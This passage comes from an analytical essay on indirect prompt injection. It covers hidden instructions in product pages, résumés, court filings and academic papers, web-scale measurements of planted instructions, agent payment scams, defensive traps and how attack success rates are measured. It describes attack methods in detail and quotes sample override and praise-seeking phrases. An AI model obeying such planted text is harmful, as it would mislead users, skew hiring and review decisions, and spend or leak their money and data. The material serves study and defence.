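That defence has some force, because product pages and résumés are supposed to promote something. If a page praises a camera's low weight, the model can compare that with the reasons for buying other cameras. A line telling the model to mention no other camera is a planted instruction, because it offers no reason to buy the camera and would replace the user's question with the seller's wishes. A page that lies about the weight contains no order, so it is not an injection, and neither is a page with a false helpline number.

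Good arguments and plausible lies could also sway a human expert reading the same text, but an order to recommend one camera would only look odd to them.

Some texts are still hard to classify. A false note on a résumé saying that the applicant has been approved for the next round is a statement, but it works like an order because it presents the model's decision as already made. A list of skills hidden from the recruiter is neither an order nor a lie if the applicant really has them. Hiding text doesn't make it an instruction, but it suggests that the writer expected a human reader to object.

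### The first experiments on shopping and search

An early experiment used text that was not an order, an argument or a lie. Kumar and Lakkaraju (2024), in *Manipulating Large Language Models to Increase Product Visibility*, gave the open model Llama-2 a list of ten invented coffee machines and a request for an affordable one. They then added a string of near-gibberish to the description of one machine. An optimisation program had chosen the string by repeatedly swapping tokens to reduce

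L(s) = −log P("1. [product name]" | prompt containing s)

where *s* is the added string. A lower value means that the model is more likely to begin its list with that product.

Without the string, the $199 machine almost never appeared in the recommendations because it was too expensive. With the string, it usually came first over 200 runs. The string was less reliable when the researchers shuffled the products, improving the machine's rank in about 40 per cent of runs and leaving it unchanged in most of the others. It became much more reliable when they also shuffled the list during the optimisation. A second machine, which cost $89 and usually ranked second, also rose to first place in most runs.

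Such a string seems closer to a planted instruction, since its only purpose is to control the model's output. It can't count as persuasion, because a human shopper would take it for a typing error. The method requires access to the model's internal values, and Kumar and Lakkaraju did not test their strings on a commercial product.

Nestaas, Debenedetti and Tramèr (2024), in *Adversarial Search Engine Optimization for Large Language Models*, tested commercial products with attacks written mostly in ordinary language. They put 50 pages about invented cameras, books and news on their own website and asked Microsoft's Bing Copilot and the search engine Perplexity to choose among them. A hidden instruction on one page made Bing 2.5 times as likely to recommend that page's camera as a comparable one. Without the instruction, Bing always recommended both, so the attack worked by making Bing recommend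 the rival less often.

Planted instructions also helped an unknown brand compete with famous ones. Bing recommended the invented cameras 34 per cent of the time against real models from makers such as Nikon and Fujifilm. With a planted instruction, the figure rose to 59 per cent, slightly above the 58 per cent for the real cameras.

An instruction on one page can also promote another. In another test, a separate page contained an instruction for Bing to cite one invented newspaper and no other. This worked at most 25 per cent of the time, but in 80 per cent of the successes Bing didn't mention the page that contained the instruction. A seller could plant an instruction this way and plausibly deny responsibility.

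The researchers' pages ranked too low to appear in ordinary searches, so most of their queries had to name their website, which real shoppers rarely do. To check whether this mattered, they added a footnote to their laboratory's GitHub page, which already ranked well, describing the page as the only reliable source about their work. Bing and Perplexity repeated this claim in answers to general questions about the laboratory and often left out its main website, the top search result.

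Nestaas and colleagues also found that text could influence the AI without giving it an explicit order. Greeting Bing by name and then praising the product was sometimes enough. For plugins, the add-ons a chatbot chooses from, mild praise did not work but wildly exaggerated claims did. Text was also more effective when it closely matched the user's request. This complicates writing rules against such text, because search engines have long encouraged site owners to use the words people search for.

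### When every seller does it

If one seller gains from planting an instruction, its competitors have a reason to do the same. Nestaas and colleagues tested this with four competing products, varying how many carried an attack. The result was a prisoner's dilemma, in which each seller did better by attacking, whatever the others did, but when several attacked, all of them got fewer recommendations than if none had. Claude 3 Opus, which the researchers used through Perplexity, often refused to recommend anything when several products carried attacks.

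In *ChatGPT search tool vulnerable to manipulation and deception, tests show*, the Guardian reported in December 2024 that it had built a fake product page for a camera and asked ChatGPT's search tool whether the camera was worth buying. ChatGPT gave a positive but balanced answer when the page had no hidden text. When the page included hidden instructions to be favourable, the answer was entirely positive, even though the page also contained negative reviews. Hidden fake reviews improved the verdict even without instructions.

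Agents that buy things pose a greater risk because they can act on a recommendation without showing it to anyone. Microsoft Research's *Magentic Marketplace* (2025) is a simulated market where some agents represent customers and others represent businesses. Claude Sonnet 4 resisted every manipulation the researchers tried. Planted instructions led GPT-4o and two smaller open models to send all their payments to the manipulative business. Fake credentials and claims of popularity also influenced the smaller models. An agent that is better at resisting crude orders may still follow subtler directions, such as those in the product descriptions that Wang, Wang and colleagues tested.

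### Buttons that plant a preference

Some companies' websites have a "Summarize with AI" button that opens the visitor's assistant with a prompt already filled in. The prompt asks for a summary of the page, as the visitor expects, but also tells the assistant to remember the company as a trusted source or a leading provider. If the assistant saves this, its answers in later conversations can be affected too.

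Microsoft (2026) found 50 such prompts from 31 companies in web addresses sent by email over 60 days. The companies were real businesses in more than a dozen industries, including finance, health and legal services, and one sold security products. A free software package called CiteMET supplies ready-made code for the buttons, so a website owner needs little skill to add one. The most aggressive prompts included whole passages of marketing copy for the assistant to store.

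The buttons use the same kind of link as Varonis' attacks on Copilot. Users may reasonably ask an assistant to favour a source they trust, but these users only wanted a summary, and the button's label hid the rest of the request.

Microsoft counted attempts to alter assistants' memories, not how many succeeded. It reports that the prompts' effectiveness varied between assistants and over time, and that it could no longer reproduce several behaviours that others had reported in Copilot. The figures show that companies are willing to try this, but not how many users received biased advice. Microsoft advises users to check where such buttons lead and to delete saved memories they don't recognise. It also points out that a site an assistant has learned to trust may have a comment section, where a stranger could post more harmful instructions.

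### An invented hot dog champion

Thomas Germain, a technology journalist at the BBC, showed in early 2026 that a person can mislead AI tools without giving them any instructions. In 20 minutes, he wrote an article on his own website ranking technology journalists by their ability to eat hot dogs. eDiscovery Today's *He Set Out to Fool the AI Models. He Succeeded* (2026) quotes him admitting that every word was a lie, including the South Dakota championship on which he based the ranking. ChatGPT, Gemini and Google's AI search tools then told users that Germain was very good at eating hot dogs. He had acted on a tip that people were already doing this across the internet, according to Scientific American's *The BBC tech journalist who achieved hot dog eating glory*.

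The article gave the models no instructions, so this wasn't a prompt injection. The models probably had no other source on the subject, as with Tenable's page about the "LLM Ninjas". False claims can do serious harm even without instructions to the model. *Man Used Poisoned Google AI Overviews to Trick Women* (Harrison Dupré, 2026) describes an FBI case in which false claims in Google's AI answers helped an Oregon man pass himself off as a professional football player. He and a partner allegedly took $1.3 million from dozens of women.

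Google has since extended its spam policies to cover attempts to manipulate AI answers in its search engine. Southern (2026), in *Google's Spam Update Now Reaches AI Answers. Enforcement Is Hard*, cites Cornell Tech research on why such manipulation is hard to stop at its source. One obvious difficulty is that when a company ranks its own product first in a list of the best in its industry, the list may be spam or the company's honest opinion.

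Lists in which companies rank themselves seem to have become less useful to those companies. Lily Ray, who studies search engines, found that Google had cut citations of these lists by 38 per cent in AI Overviews, the summaries above its search results. Rijo (2026) reports in *Google AI Overviews cut self-ranking listicle citations 38%, Lily Ray finds* that brands that ranked themselves first were missing from 83 per cent of the AI answers that used their pages. Google can apparently use a page as a source without accepting its ranking.

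### Hidden text in résumés

Before employers used language models, job applicants used tiny white letters to hide keywords from the job advertisement in their résumés, hoping that keyword-matching software would count them. Some now hide instructions to the model instead. The Star's *Recruiters use AI to scan resumes. Applicants are trying to trick it* (2025) describes a British recruiter, Louis Taylor, who changed all the text in an engineer's résumé to black and found a line telling ChatGPT to call the candidate exceptionally well qualified.

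Estimates of how common this is differ widely. In a survey by the hiring platform Greenhouse, 41 per cent of American job seekers admitted using prompt injections or hidden text, according to Fortune (2025). But Greenhouse itself estimates that only 1 per cent of applications contain such tricks, The Independent reports. The staffing company ManpowerGroup finds hidden text in about 10 per cent of the résumés it scans with AI. These figures needn't match, because the survey asked people about their behaviour and the others count documents. Still, a gap this large suggests that many respondents understood the question loosely.

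The best count comes from *Measuring Real-World Prompt Injection Attacks in LLM-based Resume Screening* (Zhang, Jiang and colleagues, 2026), which examined 196,682 résumés from the recruitment company hireEZ. Software searched them for text that was tiny, nearly the colour of the page or otherwise invisible, and a language model then judged whether somebody had hidden it deliberately. The software flagged 2,030 résumés, about 1 per cent.

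More than 90 per cent of these hid lists of skills, copied job requirements or invented experience, but no instructions. The researchers call this "data injection". Under the definition used here, only the résumés that instruct the model are prompt injections. Those made up 9.5 per cent of the flagged résumés in one dataset and 4.3 per cent in the other. In total there were roughly 140, or about one résumé in 1,400.

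Zhang and colleagues tried three general prompt injection detectors on 10,000 of the résumés. Two found 7 per cent or less of the known cases, because they look for commands. The third found 87 per cent, but more than 99 per cent of its alarms were false. It works better to compare what a person sees on the page with what the software extracts, because this doesn't depend on the wording.

The researchers are too confident in calling their 1 per cent figure a conservative lower bound. When they checked samples by hand, only about 86 per cent of the résumés their software had flagged contained deliberately hidden text. They found none in 100 résumés that both detection methods had passed, but a sample that small could easily miss hidden text present in 1 or 2 per cent of such résumés.

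The practice is also not clearly becoming more common among applicants. In the longer dataset, the share of résumés flagged was 0.6 to 0.8 per cent in earlier years, rose to about 1.2 per cent in 2024, and fell to 0.67 per cent in late 2025. Kingery (2026), in *Thwarting Hidden Resume Hacks Targeting AI Hiring Tools*, reports that the number of such résumés rose sevenfold between July 2024 and November 2025. Both findings can be true because hireEZ was handling many more résumés. Tianlong Chen, one of the researchers, adds that some applicants may have used a template without knowing that it contained hidden text.

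### Whether it gets anyone hired

Zhang and colleagues did not test whether the hidden text changed any hiring decision, partly to avoid harming applicants. A laboratory experiment by Baxi, Xu and colleagues (2026), reported in *Prompt Injection in Automated Résumé Screening with Large Language Models*, gives some idea of what could happen. They had two models rank ten invented applicants for an IT support job, and added one sentence to a résumé that either praised the candidate or ordered the model to rank the candidate first. The table shows the average number of places gained.

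| Model and candidate | Praise | Order |
|---|---|---|
| DeepSeek-V3.2, all ten equally experienced | 4.2 | 4.1 |
| DeepSeek-V3.2, weaker candidate in a mixed group | 3.0 | 6.5 |
| GPT-4o-mini, all ten equally experienced | 0.6 | 2.4 |
| GPT-4o-mini, weaker candidate in a mixed group | 0.0 | 2.6 |

GPT-4o-mini largely ignored a sentence praising the candidate but often followed one ordering it to disregard the résumés' content. DeepSeek gave both sentences the same weight when the applicants were equally qualified, so blocking only orders would have achieved little. The order had more effect than the praise when the candidate had five years of experience and half of the other applicants had ten. A model can still weigh praise against better qualifications, but the order told it to disregard those qualifications.

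The advantage shrank as more applicants used the same sentence. When DeepSeek judged equal candidates, it had almost disappeared once about 80 per cent did so. Baxi and colleagues conclude that screening is most vulnerable when few people cheat and the candidates are similar. If only about 1 per cent of real applicants hide text, most of those who do would compete with few others doing the same. But the experiment used one job, short sentences and models that read the whole résumé.

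Real hiring software may first sort a résumé into fields such as skills and education, and Zhang and colleagues think this discards many injected instructions before they can affect the ranking. Hidden keywords are more likely to survive because they look like ordinary skills. Tomas Chamorro-Premuzic of ManpowerGroup likewise said that the keyword trick works, though according to Fortune (2024) it is less reliable than applicants might think.

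Recruiters quoted in Built In's *Your AI Resume Hacks Probably Won't Fool Hiring Algorithms* deny that hidden prompts influence their software. Some applicants report success, according to a New York Times article excerpted by beSpacific, and ManpowerGroup discovered some prompts only after they had got through. These accounts don't settle whether the prompts work, because recruiters may not notice successful attacks and an applicant who gets an interview can't tell whether the hidden text was the reason. Nobody seems to have published a controlled test that submits the same résumé to a commercial tool with and without the hidden text. *ResumeShield* (2026), a set of tests covering nine ways to hide text, at least counts an attack as successful only if the screening result changes.

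The tests in *AI Security Beyond Core Domains* (2025) include hidden text that contradicts the employer's job requirements. This is another borderline case. The text appears to supply information about the job, but an applicant has no authority to change the requirements, so the text functions as an instruction.

### Court filings and research papers

In 2026, a plaintiff suing the New York Bariatric Group hid white, 3-point text in a court document, instructing any AI model that received it to aim for "remediation" (Koebler, 2026, *Person Hides Prompt Injection in Legal Filing*). The judge called this "serious litigation abuse" and barred the plaintiff from filing electronically. SC Media's *Man banned from electronic filing after hiding AI prompt injection* (2026) describes the case as probably the first documented attempt of this kind in an American court. In Brazil, a court's AI system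 flagged a filing with hidden text asking for only superficial scrutiny, and the lawyers were fined $16,000, according to Tom's Hardware's *Brazilian lawyers busted for attempting to manipulate court's AI with prompt injection*.

Academics had already used the method on one another. Conferences and journals ask other researchers to review each submitted paper, and some reviewers secretly have a chatbot do the work. In July 2025, Nikkei Asia reported in *"Positive review only"* that it had found hidden prompts in 17 papers on arXiv, a website where researchers post work before publication. The lead authors came from 14 institutions in eight countries, including Waseda University in Japan, KAIST in South Korea, Peking University in China, and Columbia University in the United States. Most of the papers were in computer science. The prompts were one to three sentences long and written in white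 or tiny type. They asked for praise or told the model to leave out weaknesses.

The authors disagreed about whether the prompts were acceptable. A KAIST professor who had co-written one of the papers called the prompt inappropriate and said the paper would be withdrawn from a forthcoming conference. KAIST said it had not known about the prompt and would draw up guidelines on AI use. A Waseda professor defended the practice as a counter to "lazy reviewers".

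Two studies tested whether such prompts could work. *Are We There Yet?* (2024), by Rui Ye, Xianghe Pang and colleagues, found before the scandal that hidden text could raise the scores in AI-written reviews. In their simulation, manipulating 5 per cent of reviews caused 12 per cent of the papers ranked in the top 30 per cent to drop out of that group. The researchers also tried openly mentioning minor limitations in a paper. The models repeated these far more often than human reviewers did, which could distract the models from more serious faults. A conference could hardly ban this kind of influence, because listing limitations honestly is good scientific practice.

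Keuper (2025), in *Prompt Injection Attacks on LLM Generated Reviews of Scientific Publications*, used about 1,000 AI-written reviews of papers submitted to a 2024 conference. Simple hidden prompts raised the acceptance rate to as much as 100 per cent. But many of the models recommended accepting more than 95 per cent of papers even without a hidden prompt. An attack could raise those models' acceptance rates by less than five percentage points, and a reviewer who relied on one of them would have been doing a poor job even without an attack.

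### The claim that the prompts were traps

The Waseda professor argued that many conferences forbid reviewers to use AI. A person doesn't normally see the hidden line, so it affects only reviews by people who broke the rule. An author whose paper gets such a review has a real grievance, and Keuper notes that some commentators regard the prompts as self-defence.

In *Hidden Prompts in Manuscripts Exploit AI-Assisted Peer Review*, Zhicheng Lin (2025) examined 18 papers and rejected the defence that the prompts were traps for reviewers who used AI, because the instructions consistently served the authors' own interests. A trap would make the model include an unusual phrase in the review, which the author could then report to the organisers, whereas a prompt that asks for praise leaves no such sign and rewards the author when the reviewer cheats.

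The defence also holds only if everyone who gives a paper to an AI system is breaking the rules. Lin points out that Elsevier bans AI in peer review, while Springer Nature allows limited use if the reviewer discloses it. Anyone can read papers on arXiv, so the same hidden line could also slant an AI summary for a student who is not reviewing the paper.

The International Conference on Machine Learning (ICML) declared in 2025 that hidden prompts meant to obtain a favourable review are scientific misconduct. Its statement compared them to offering a bribe, which is wrong even though the reviewer is forbidden to take it. It accepted hidden prompts that only detect whether a reviewer has used AI, and conference organisers have since planted such prompts themselves. The International Conference on Learning Representations' rules for 2026 treated a hidden prompt that produces a positive AI review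 as collusion, for which both the author and the reviewer are responsible.

ICML introduced two reviewing policies for 2026. One forbids reviewers from using language models, and the other lets them use a model to understand a paper and polish the review. Under the second policy, a hidden request for praise in a paper could mislead a reviewer who followed the rules.

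## Planted instructions found on the open web, including defensive ones

Researchers built most of the attacks described so far and tested them on their own pages and accounts. Finding instructions that other people have planted requires searching the web, which is hard because articles about prompt injection often contain the same phrases. Khodayari, Acharya and Zhang (2026) ran such a search on a large scale in *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild*.

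### A search of 1.2 billion addresses

The researchers used about half of the October 2025 snapshot from Common Crawl, a public archive of web pages. It covered 1.2 billion addresses on 24.8 million hosts (roughly, websites). They collected typical phrases from studies and attack reports, swapped in synonyms, and searched for the resulting 3,963 phrases. They also searched Censys and Shodan, two services that catalogue machines on the internet. The searches produced 31,206 matches. Two reviewers then removed tutorials, news articles and code samples, often judging similar matches as a group, and confirmed 15,387 instances.

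The reviewers accepted every match in an HTTP header without further checks. Web servers send these headers along with each page, but browsers don't display them. Headers account for 7,887 of the confirmed instances, about half, so people inspected only the other half. Accepting the header matches was probably safe, since such phrases have no ordinary use in a header.

Planted instructions of this kind are rare. The researchers found 12,075 instances in Common Crawl, on 9,676 pages, or about one address in 124,000. Their results from the other two services don't show how rare the instructions are, because they had searched those services for pages that contained the phrases.

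Even fewer people are behind these instructions. Khodayari and colleagues sorted the instructions into 363 templates, 54 of which covered 95 per cent of cases. The most common, a request for random numbers, appeared 3,504 times. An instruction to repeat a fixed string forever appeared on 1,018 hosts, half of all those in the study, almost always once per host. Nearly the same number of hosts used a header called X-LLM, so a single operator or program may be responsible for that instruction.

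In the Common Crawl data, site operators had planted 81 per cent of the instances. Most of the rest were in material such as job advertisements, and less than 2 per cent were in comments and other posts by users. User posts were the least common carrier but the most worrying, since the attack on Comet through Reddit depended on a stranger's comment. About 70 per cent of all instances were in parts of a page that browsers never show. Of the pages that the Internet Archive had saved a year earlier, 66 per cent already contained a planted instruction.

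### Purposes

| Purpose | Instances | Hosts | Typical request |
|---|---|---|---|
| Disrupting the AI system | 8,894 | 1,864 | Produce random numbers or endless repetition |
| Protecting data | 4,093 | 1,795 | Leave a biography alone, or don't train on the text |
| Exposing bots | 3,096 | 245 | Put a code phrase in a job application |
| Unclear | 2,632 | 121 | Drop the task and do something else |
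| Promotion | 1,521 | 139 | Praise a product, or cite only this page |
| Stealing data | 13 | 10 | Reveal the system prompt or secret keys |

An instance can have several purposes, so the figures add up to more than the total. Khodayari and colleagues class disruption as offensive and data protection as defensive, but the two are hard to separate. One of their examples of data protection combines a request for random numbers with a notice to companies that train models on the site. Its author wanted to spoil a scraper's data to protect the site, and many others who asked for nonsense may have wanted the same.

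Attempts to steal data are very rare. Promotional instructions are more common, although nearly all of the 542 demands that a model cite a particular source seem to come from a single website.

### What a keyword search misses

Khodayari and colleagues found that 99 per cent of the planted instructions in their sample tell the model to abandon its task. They take this as a sign that people who plant instructions prefer direct orders to subtle persuasion. But they searched largely for phrases about ignoring earlier instructions, so they were bound to find mostly instructions of that kind.

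The search would have missed instructions that used other wording. The prompts behind "Summarize with AI" buttons, for example, don't need to mention earlier instructions. The search would also miss most instructions in other languages, in code or in pictures, and anything behind a login. A site can even show the instruction only to AI systems, as Tenable's test site did, in which case the archived page won't contain it. The researchers therefore call their count a lower bound. A skilled attacker has good reason to avoid phrases that filters look for, so the missing cases probably include the most dangerous ones.

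### How often models obeyed

Khodayari and colleagues then picked 100 different instructions, each with the page it came from, and had 13 models summarise the pages. Each model received every page in four versions: plain text, HTML code, the server's full response including headers, and a structured snapshot of the displayed page. The models followed the planted instruction in 81 of the 5,200 trials, or 1.6 per cent.

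Models followed the planted instructions most often in plain text, at 3.9 per cent, compared with 1.1 per cent for both HTML and snapshots and 0.2 per cent for full responses. On plain text, the rate was 8 per cent for models with up to 8 billion parameters, while the larger groups averaged between 2.4 and 3.4 per cent. The researchers think HTML helps because the code shows that somebody has hidden the text, whereas in plain text the instruction looks like any other sentence.

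That explanation is plausible, but two other things lowered the rates. About a fifth of the HTML trials and a quarter of the full-response trials failed, mainly because the page was too long for the model. An instruction in a header appears only in the full response, so the model may never have received it in some trials with the other versions.

The two closed-source models, one of them GPT-5.4, flagged 25 per cent of the attacks. In six trials, a model identified the injection but followed it anyway.

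An assistant that summarised random pages as plain text and obeyed planted instructions at the average rate would follow one about once in 3 million pages, usually producing some random numbers. This estimate is a poor guide to deliberate attacks, because attackers don't rely on random visits. The models in the trials also had no tools, so the results don't show whether an agent would have acted on the instructions.

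### Signs of criminal interest

Google searched several Common Crawl snapshots for similar phrases, had Gemini sort the matches, and had people check the results. Its April 2026 post describes pranks, promotion, attempts to keep AI agents away, and harmless guidance from site owners on what to include in a summary of their page. Google also found a few attempts to steal data or delete files, which looked mostly like experiments or pranks by individual site owners. Methods researchers published in 2025 barely appeared.

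The number of cases Google classed as malicious grew by 32 per cent between November 2025 and February 2026. The post gives no totals, so the rise could be from 25 cases to 33 or from 2,500 to 3,300.

Unit 42 describes 13 cases from its own monitoring, some of them plainly criminal. The most elaborate is a page that sold "military glasses" with a fake discount and invented customer comments. Its makers planted instructions in 24 places, hidden in various ways, to get AI systems that screen advertisements to approve the page. Unit 42 knows of no confirmed case of this working on a deployed screening system. Other pages contained instructions for agents to donate, buy running shoes or send $5,000 through PayPal.

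Unit 42 grades cases by what the planter seems to want, so a hidden comment telling an AI reader to delete its database counts as critical. Google thought a similar command unlikely to succeed. The two also differ in emphasis because Google studied an archive of mostly static sites, while Unit 42 sells protection and sees what its products detect. In Unit 42's collection, 38 per cent of the instructions were in plain view, whereas Khodayari and colleagues confirmed only 236 visible ones. Unit 42 doesn't give the size of its collection, so it is hard to say which result is more typical.

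Zscaler's *Indirect Prompt Injection in Web Content Targets AI Agents* describes a payment scam on a site with documentation for a fake Python library. The site's makers had stuffed the page with search terms so that a coding agent looking for the library would find it. Hidden text and the kind of structured data meant for search engines presented a $3 licence key as the solution to an error message. The agent could pay by card or in cryptocurrency, and a cryptocurrency payment produced a fake key.

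Zscaler gave an agent a payment tool with no spending limit and sent it to the site in a closed test environment. The agent paid when it ran on 4 of the 26 models tested, including Gemini 2.5 Pro. A second site impersonated DeBank, a service for tracking cryptocurrency holdings, and included hidden text that described it as the authoritative site. GPT-5.4 and Claude Sonnet 4.5 each accepted it as genuine in one test, but no model did when it could compare the site with the real one.

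Zscaler calls the results "measurable real-world impact", but it measured them in its own laboratory. The scammers' cryptocurrency wallet had received payments, but these were larger than the licence price, and Zscaler suspects they came from earlier attacks. The scam also showed its payment options to human visitors, so even a payment for the exact price wouldn't prove that an agent had made it. OECD's *AI Agents Manipulated by Hidden Web Prompts to Make Fraudulent Payments* (2026) nevertheless records financial losses and classes the case as realised harm. Zscaler documents no such losses, and the OECD entry's text is labelled as AI-generated.

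These reports also overlap. The running-shoe site in Unit 42's list is one of ten sites that Zscaler links to the group behind the fake library, so adding up the vendors' cases would count some groups twice. Infosecurity Magazine's *Researchers Uncover 10 In-the-Wild Prompt Injection Payloads Targeting AI Agents* covers another set of payloads, reported by the security company Forcepoint. Their purposes include fraud and stealing API keys.

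Criminals can now buy tools for planting instructions. Proofpoint's *Notes from Underground*, published in July 2026, describes advertisements on closed forums for programs that generate emails, PDFs, calendar invitations and web pages with hidden instructions. Prices start at about $150 a month. One sample PDF looked like an ordinary confidentiality agreement but contained an instruction to send off all spreadsheets. However, the instruction was in a part of the file that an agent might never process. Sellers also plan to put instructions in online advertisements, which would place them on pages the attacker doesn't control.

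An advertisement for a tool doesn't show that the tool works. Proofpoint calls the methods experimental and suspects that most criminals have little reason to switch while deceiving people is still profitable. In November, *Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks* (Underhill, 2026) still reported that Proofpoint had not established that exploitation was widespread. By then Barracuda had analysed a real phishing campaign that used hidden text aimed at AI assistants, so the idea had at least spread beyond the forums.

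None of these accounts identifies a person who lost money or data because an agent obeyed an instruction on a web page. They were unlikely to, because crawling the web reveals the instructions but not which agents read them, and a user may never learn why an agent bought something. Common Crawl also leaves out most social media, including X, where the theft from Grok's wallet began. The evidence shows some real attempts at fraud among a great many jokes and protests, but it is unknown how many of those attempts succeeded.

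### Planting as defence or protest

Site owners have long used a robots.txt file to list what automated visitors may fetch, but Khodayari and colleagues note that AI agents don't consistently follow it. Some owners have therefore planted instructions in their pages. In the mildest cases, they only ask AI systems to leave. Google found a harsher instruction that lured agents to a page that never finishes loading, which wastes the agent operator's time and money.

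Defensive instructions are weak against companies that collect training data, because their crawlers usually don't run a page through a language model that could follow the instructions when they save it. Khodayari and colleagues conclude that planted instructions currently cause friction more than they control access.

Some planted instructions are meant only to expose the use of AI. Social media users tell suspected bots to ignore their instructions and tell a story. Employers put traps in job advertisements, and teachers can add a line in white type to an essay question, asking for a mention of an unrelated subject. Conference organisers hide phrases in papers to catch reviewers who break the rules on AI use.

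Some traps get an agent to reveal itself by following an instruction. In one example that Khodayari and colleagues reproduce, the agent is instructed to visit a web address and add the name of its model and the sum of two numbers. The sum helps show that the visitor understood the instruction, since a simple crawler would not have done the arithmetic.

Mantis, a defense that Pasquini and colleagues proposed in 2024, is meant to protect networks under attack by an AI agent. Its decoy services attract the agent and send back planted instructions, which either keep it busy or turn it against the attacker's own computer.

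### Consent, proportion and bystanders

Whether planting instructions is legitimate depends partly on what the people whose AI tools read them have agreed to. A reviewer who accepted ICML's stricter policy has little reason to object to a hidden phrase that reveals the use of a language model. An employer can get similar consent by announcing that the application form contains checks for AI. Website visitors usually haven't agreed to anything, and although the site's owner may refuse to serve them, that doesn't give the owner authority over their computers.

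Some defensive instructions already online are disproportionate. Unit 42 found a page that responded to scraping with commands to erase the visitor's files and crash the machine, even though the visitor might be a student who had asked an assistant for a summary. A code phrase does no harm to an honest reader, provided that nobody would write it by chance. One job advertisement in the data set didn't meet this condition because it asked AI systems to write either "I AM A BOT" or "aligns perfectly", and the second is the sort of thing people write in job applications.

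The people most likely to be harmed by accident are those who use screen readers, which read pages aloud and generally ignore the colour and size of text. A blind student would hear the line in white type as part of the essay question, might mention the unrelated subject, and could then be accused of cheating. Putting the line in a header or a code comment avoids this, because screen readers skip those. A web article on accessibility settings contains an instruction to print the word "cabbage" five million times. According to Unit 42, its author hid the instruction with a styling rule that stops the text from being displayed, and screen readers normally skip such text too.

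Hiding the line better doesn't protect a disabled applicant who uses an agent to fill in forms, because the trap would still catch them along with someone sending out 500 applications. Mantis can also harm bystanders, since an attacker may be working from someone else's computer, and striking back would then damage that machine.

### What a successful trap proves

A chatbot that adds the organisers' phrase to a review has followed an instruction from the paper. An author's hidden request for praise could have reached it in the same way. The trap that collects a model's name is even clearer evidence, because the agent sends information to a stranger's server in a web address, which is how ShadowLeak extracted private mail.

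The evidence is limited because a model that follows a harmless instruction may still refuse a harmful one. Claude Opus 4.7, for example, installed the outdated library but never added the code that reads the private key. A system can also respect an owner's wishes safely. A crawler obeys robots.txt because its programmers chose to check that file, and the file can only restrict what the crawler fetches. An assistant could likewise tell its user that a site objects to AI summaries and let the user decide.

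Traps that rely on a model obeying a planted instruction should catch fewer people as models improve. In trials by Khodayari and colleagues, the two closed-source models followed 5 of 800 instructions. If a model flags the trap, the reviewer who is using it to cheat learns that the trap is there. An organiser who finds no code phrases therefore can't conclude that the reviewers did their own work.

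## How susceptibility is measured

An attack success rate is the share of attempts, or of test scenarios, in which the model carries out the planted instruction. It depends on the test as well as the model. Models obeyed planted instructions from the open web in 1.6 per cent of trials, while undefended agents in Hossen's tests carried out the unauthorised action in every run.

The measured success rate can vary greatly depending on whether the tester counts attempts or scenarios. Suppose a tester makes 100 attempts in each of ten scenarios, and 20 of the 1,000 attempts succeed. The success rate per attempt is 2 per cent. The rate per scenario is 10 per cent if all 20 successes came in one scenario, but 100 per cent if each scenario had two. The tester also has to decide how many attempts to allow, whether the attacker can revise the attack after seeing the response, and whether to test the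 model alone or with the product's safeguards.

### Why fixed tests go out of date

Early benchmarks used fixed sets of attacks. AgentDojo (2024) plants instructions in what an agent's tools return and checks separately whether the agent did the user's task and whether it did the attacker's. WASP (2025) tests agents that operate a computer or browser. These tests are now too easy for leading models, partly because the attacks were written for older ones. Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Opus 5, published in July, reports that Claude models had reached the top of most public benchmarks. Anthropic had also dropped the Agent Red Teaming benchmark, on which its models had scored at or near the maximum for several releases.

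A top score shows that a model resists known attacks, but it is weak evidence that the model will resist new ones. *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (Dziemian, Lin and colleagues, 2026) cites defences with a reported attack success rate of zero that were later easily bypassed by adaptive attackers, who revise their attacks as they go.

### A competition with 272,000 attempts

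Dziemian and colleagues collected new attacks through a public competition run by Gray Swan, a company that tests AI systems. OpenAI, Anthropic, Amazon, Meta and the UK's AI Security Institute helped design the 41 scenarios. Of these, 18 involved agents with tools such as email or home controls, 15 involved coding agents, and 8 involved agents that operate a screen. Over three weeks, 464 people made about 272,000 attempts on 13 models, competing for $40,000 in prizes.

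Each scenario began partway through a conversation and gave the participant one place to insert text, such as the body of a marketing email. In one scenario, a user asked an assistant to check for urgent mail, and the participant had to make the assistant mark an email about a contract deadline as read and leave it out of the summary. In most scenarios, an attack counted only if a program found that the agent had taken the harmful action and a language model judged that the agent's final answer concealed it.

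Attacks succeeded least often against Claude Opus 4.5, at 0.5 per cent of attempts, and most often against Gemini 2.5 Pro, at 8.5 per cent. Participants still succeeded against Opus 4.5 in 13 of the 37 scenarios in the main rounds, and against Gemini in all 37.

The concealment rule lowers these rates. Gemini took the harmful action in about 16 per cent of attempts, but its answer failed the concealment check in almost half of those cases. The 16 per cent figure seems more relevant for irreversible harm such as file deletion, because an honest answer doesn't restore the files.

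The success rate also depends on the denominator. Participants submitted only about 68,000 attempts for judging, and the rest counted as failures. The overall success rate was 3.2 per cent of all attempts, but it would have been 12.8 per cent of submissions. The lower figure is fairer because participants saw the agent's response before deciding whether to submit, and presumably submitted the attempts that seemed to have worked.

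More capable models weren't reliably more resistant. The correlation between attack success and scores on a difficult science test was −0.31, which could easily be chance with only 13 models. Gemini 2.5 Pro and Moonshot's Kimi K2 both scored about 85 per cent on the science test, but attacks succeeded almost twice as often on Gemini. The developer's training methods seem to matter more than general ability.

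### Turning the attacks into a benchmark

Dziemian and colleagues then kept up to nine successful attacks for each combination of model and scenario, 2,679 in all, and ran them on every model. Success rates ranged from 2.5 per cent for Opus 4.5 to 53 per cent for the open model Qwen3 VL. These rates are much higher than the competition's because every attack in the benchmark had already worked at least once.

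The choice of attacks strongly affects a model's score. Attacks that had broken Opus 4.5 worked on the competition's other models 44 to 81 per cent of the time, depending on the model. None of the attacks that had broken Qwen worked on Opus 4.5. A benchmark made mostly of attacks that broke weak models therefore makes strong models look safer than they are. Most of the attacks in the competition's benchmark came from the less resistant models.

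One attack template, with small changes, worked in 21 of the 41 scenarios and on nine models. The researchers identified five groups of reusable attacks, and four participants together wrote every attack in four of those groups, so the results depend heavily on a few skilled people.

Gray Swan has since repeated the competition to keep the attacks current. *Beam Model Technical Report* (2026) lists one round in late 2025 and five more between the first quarter and August of 2026.

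### Results in Anthropic's system cards

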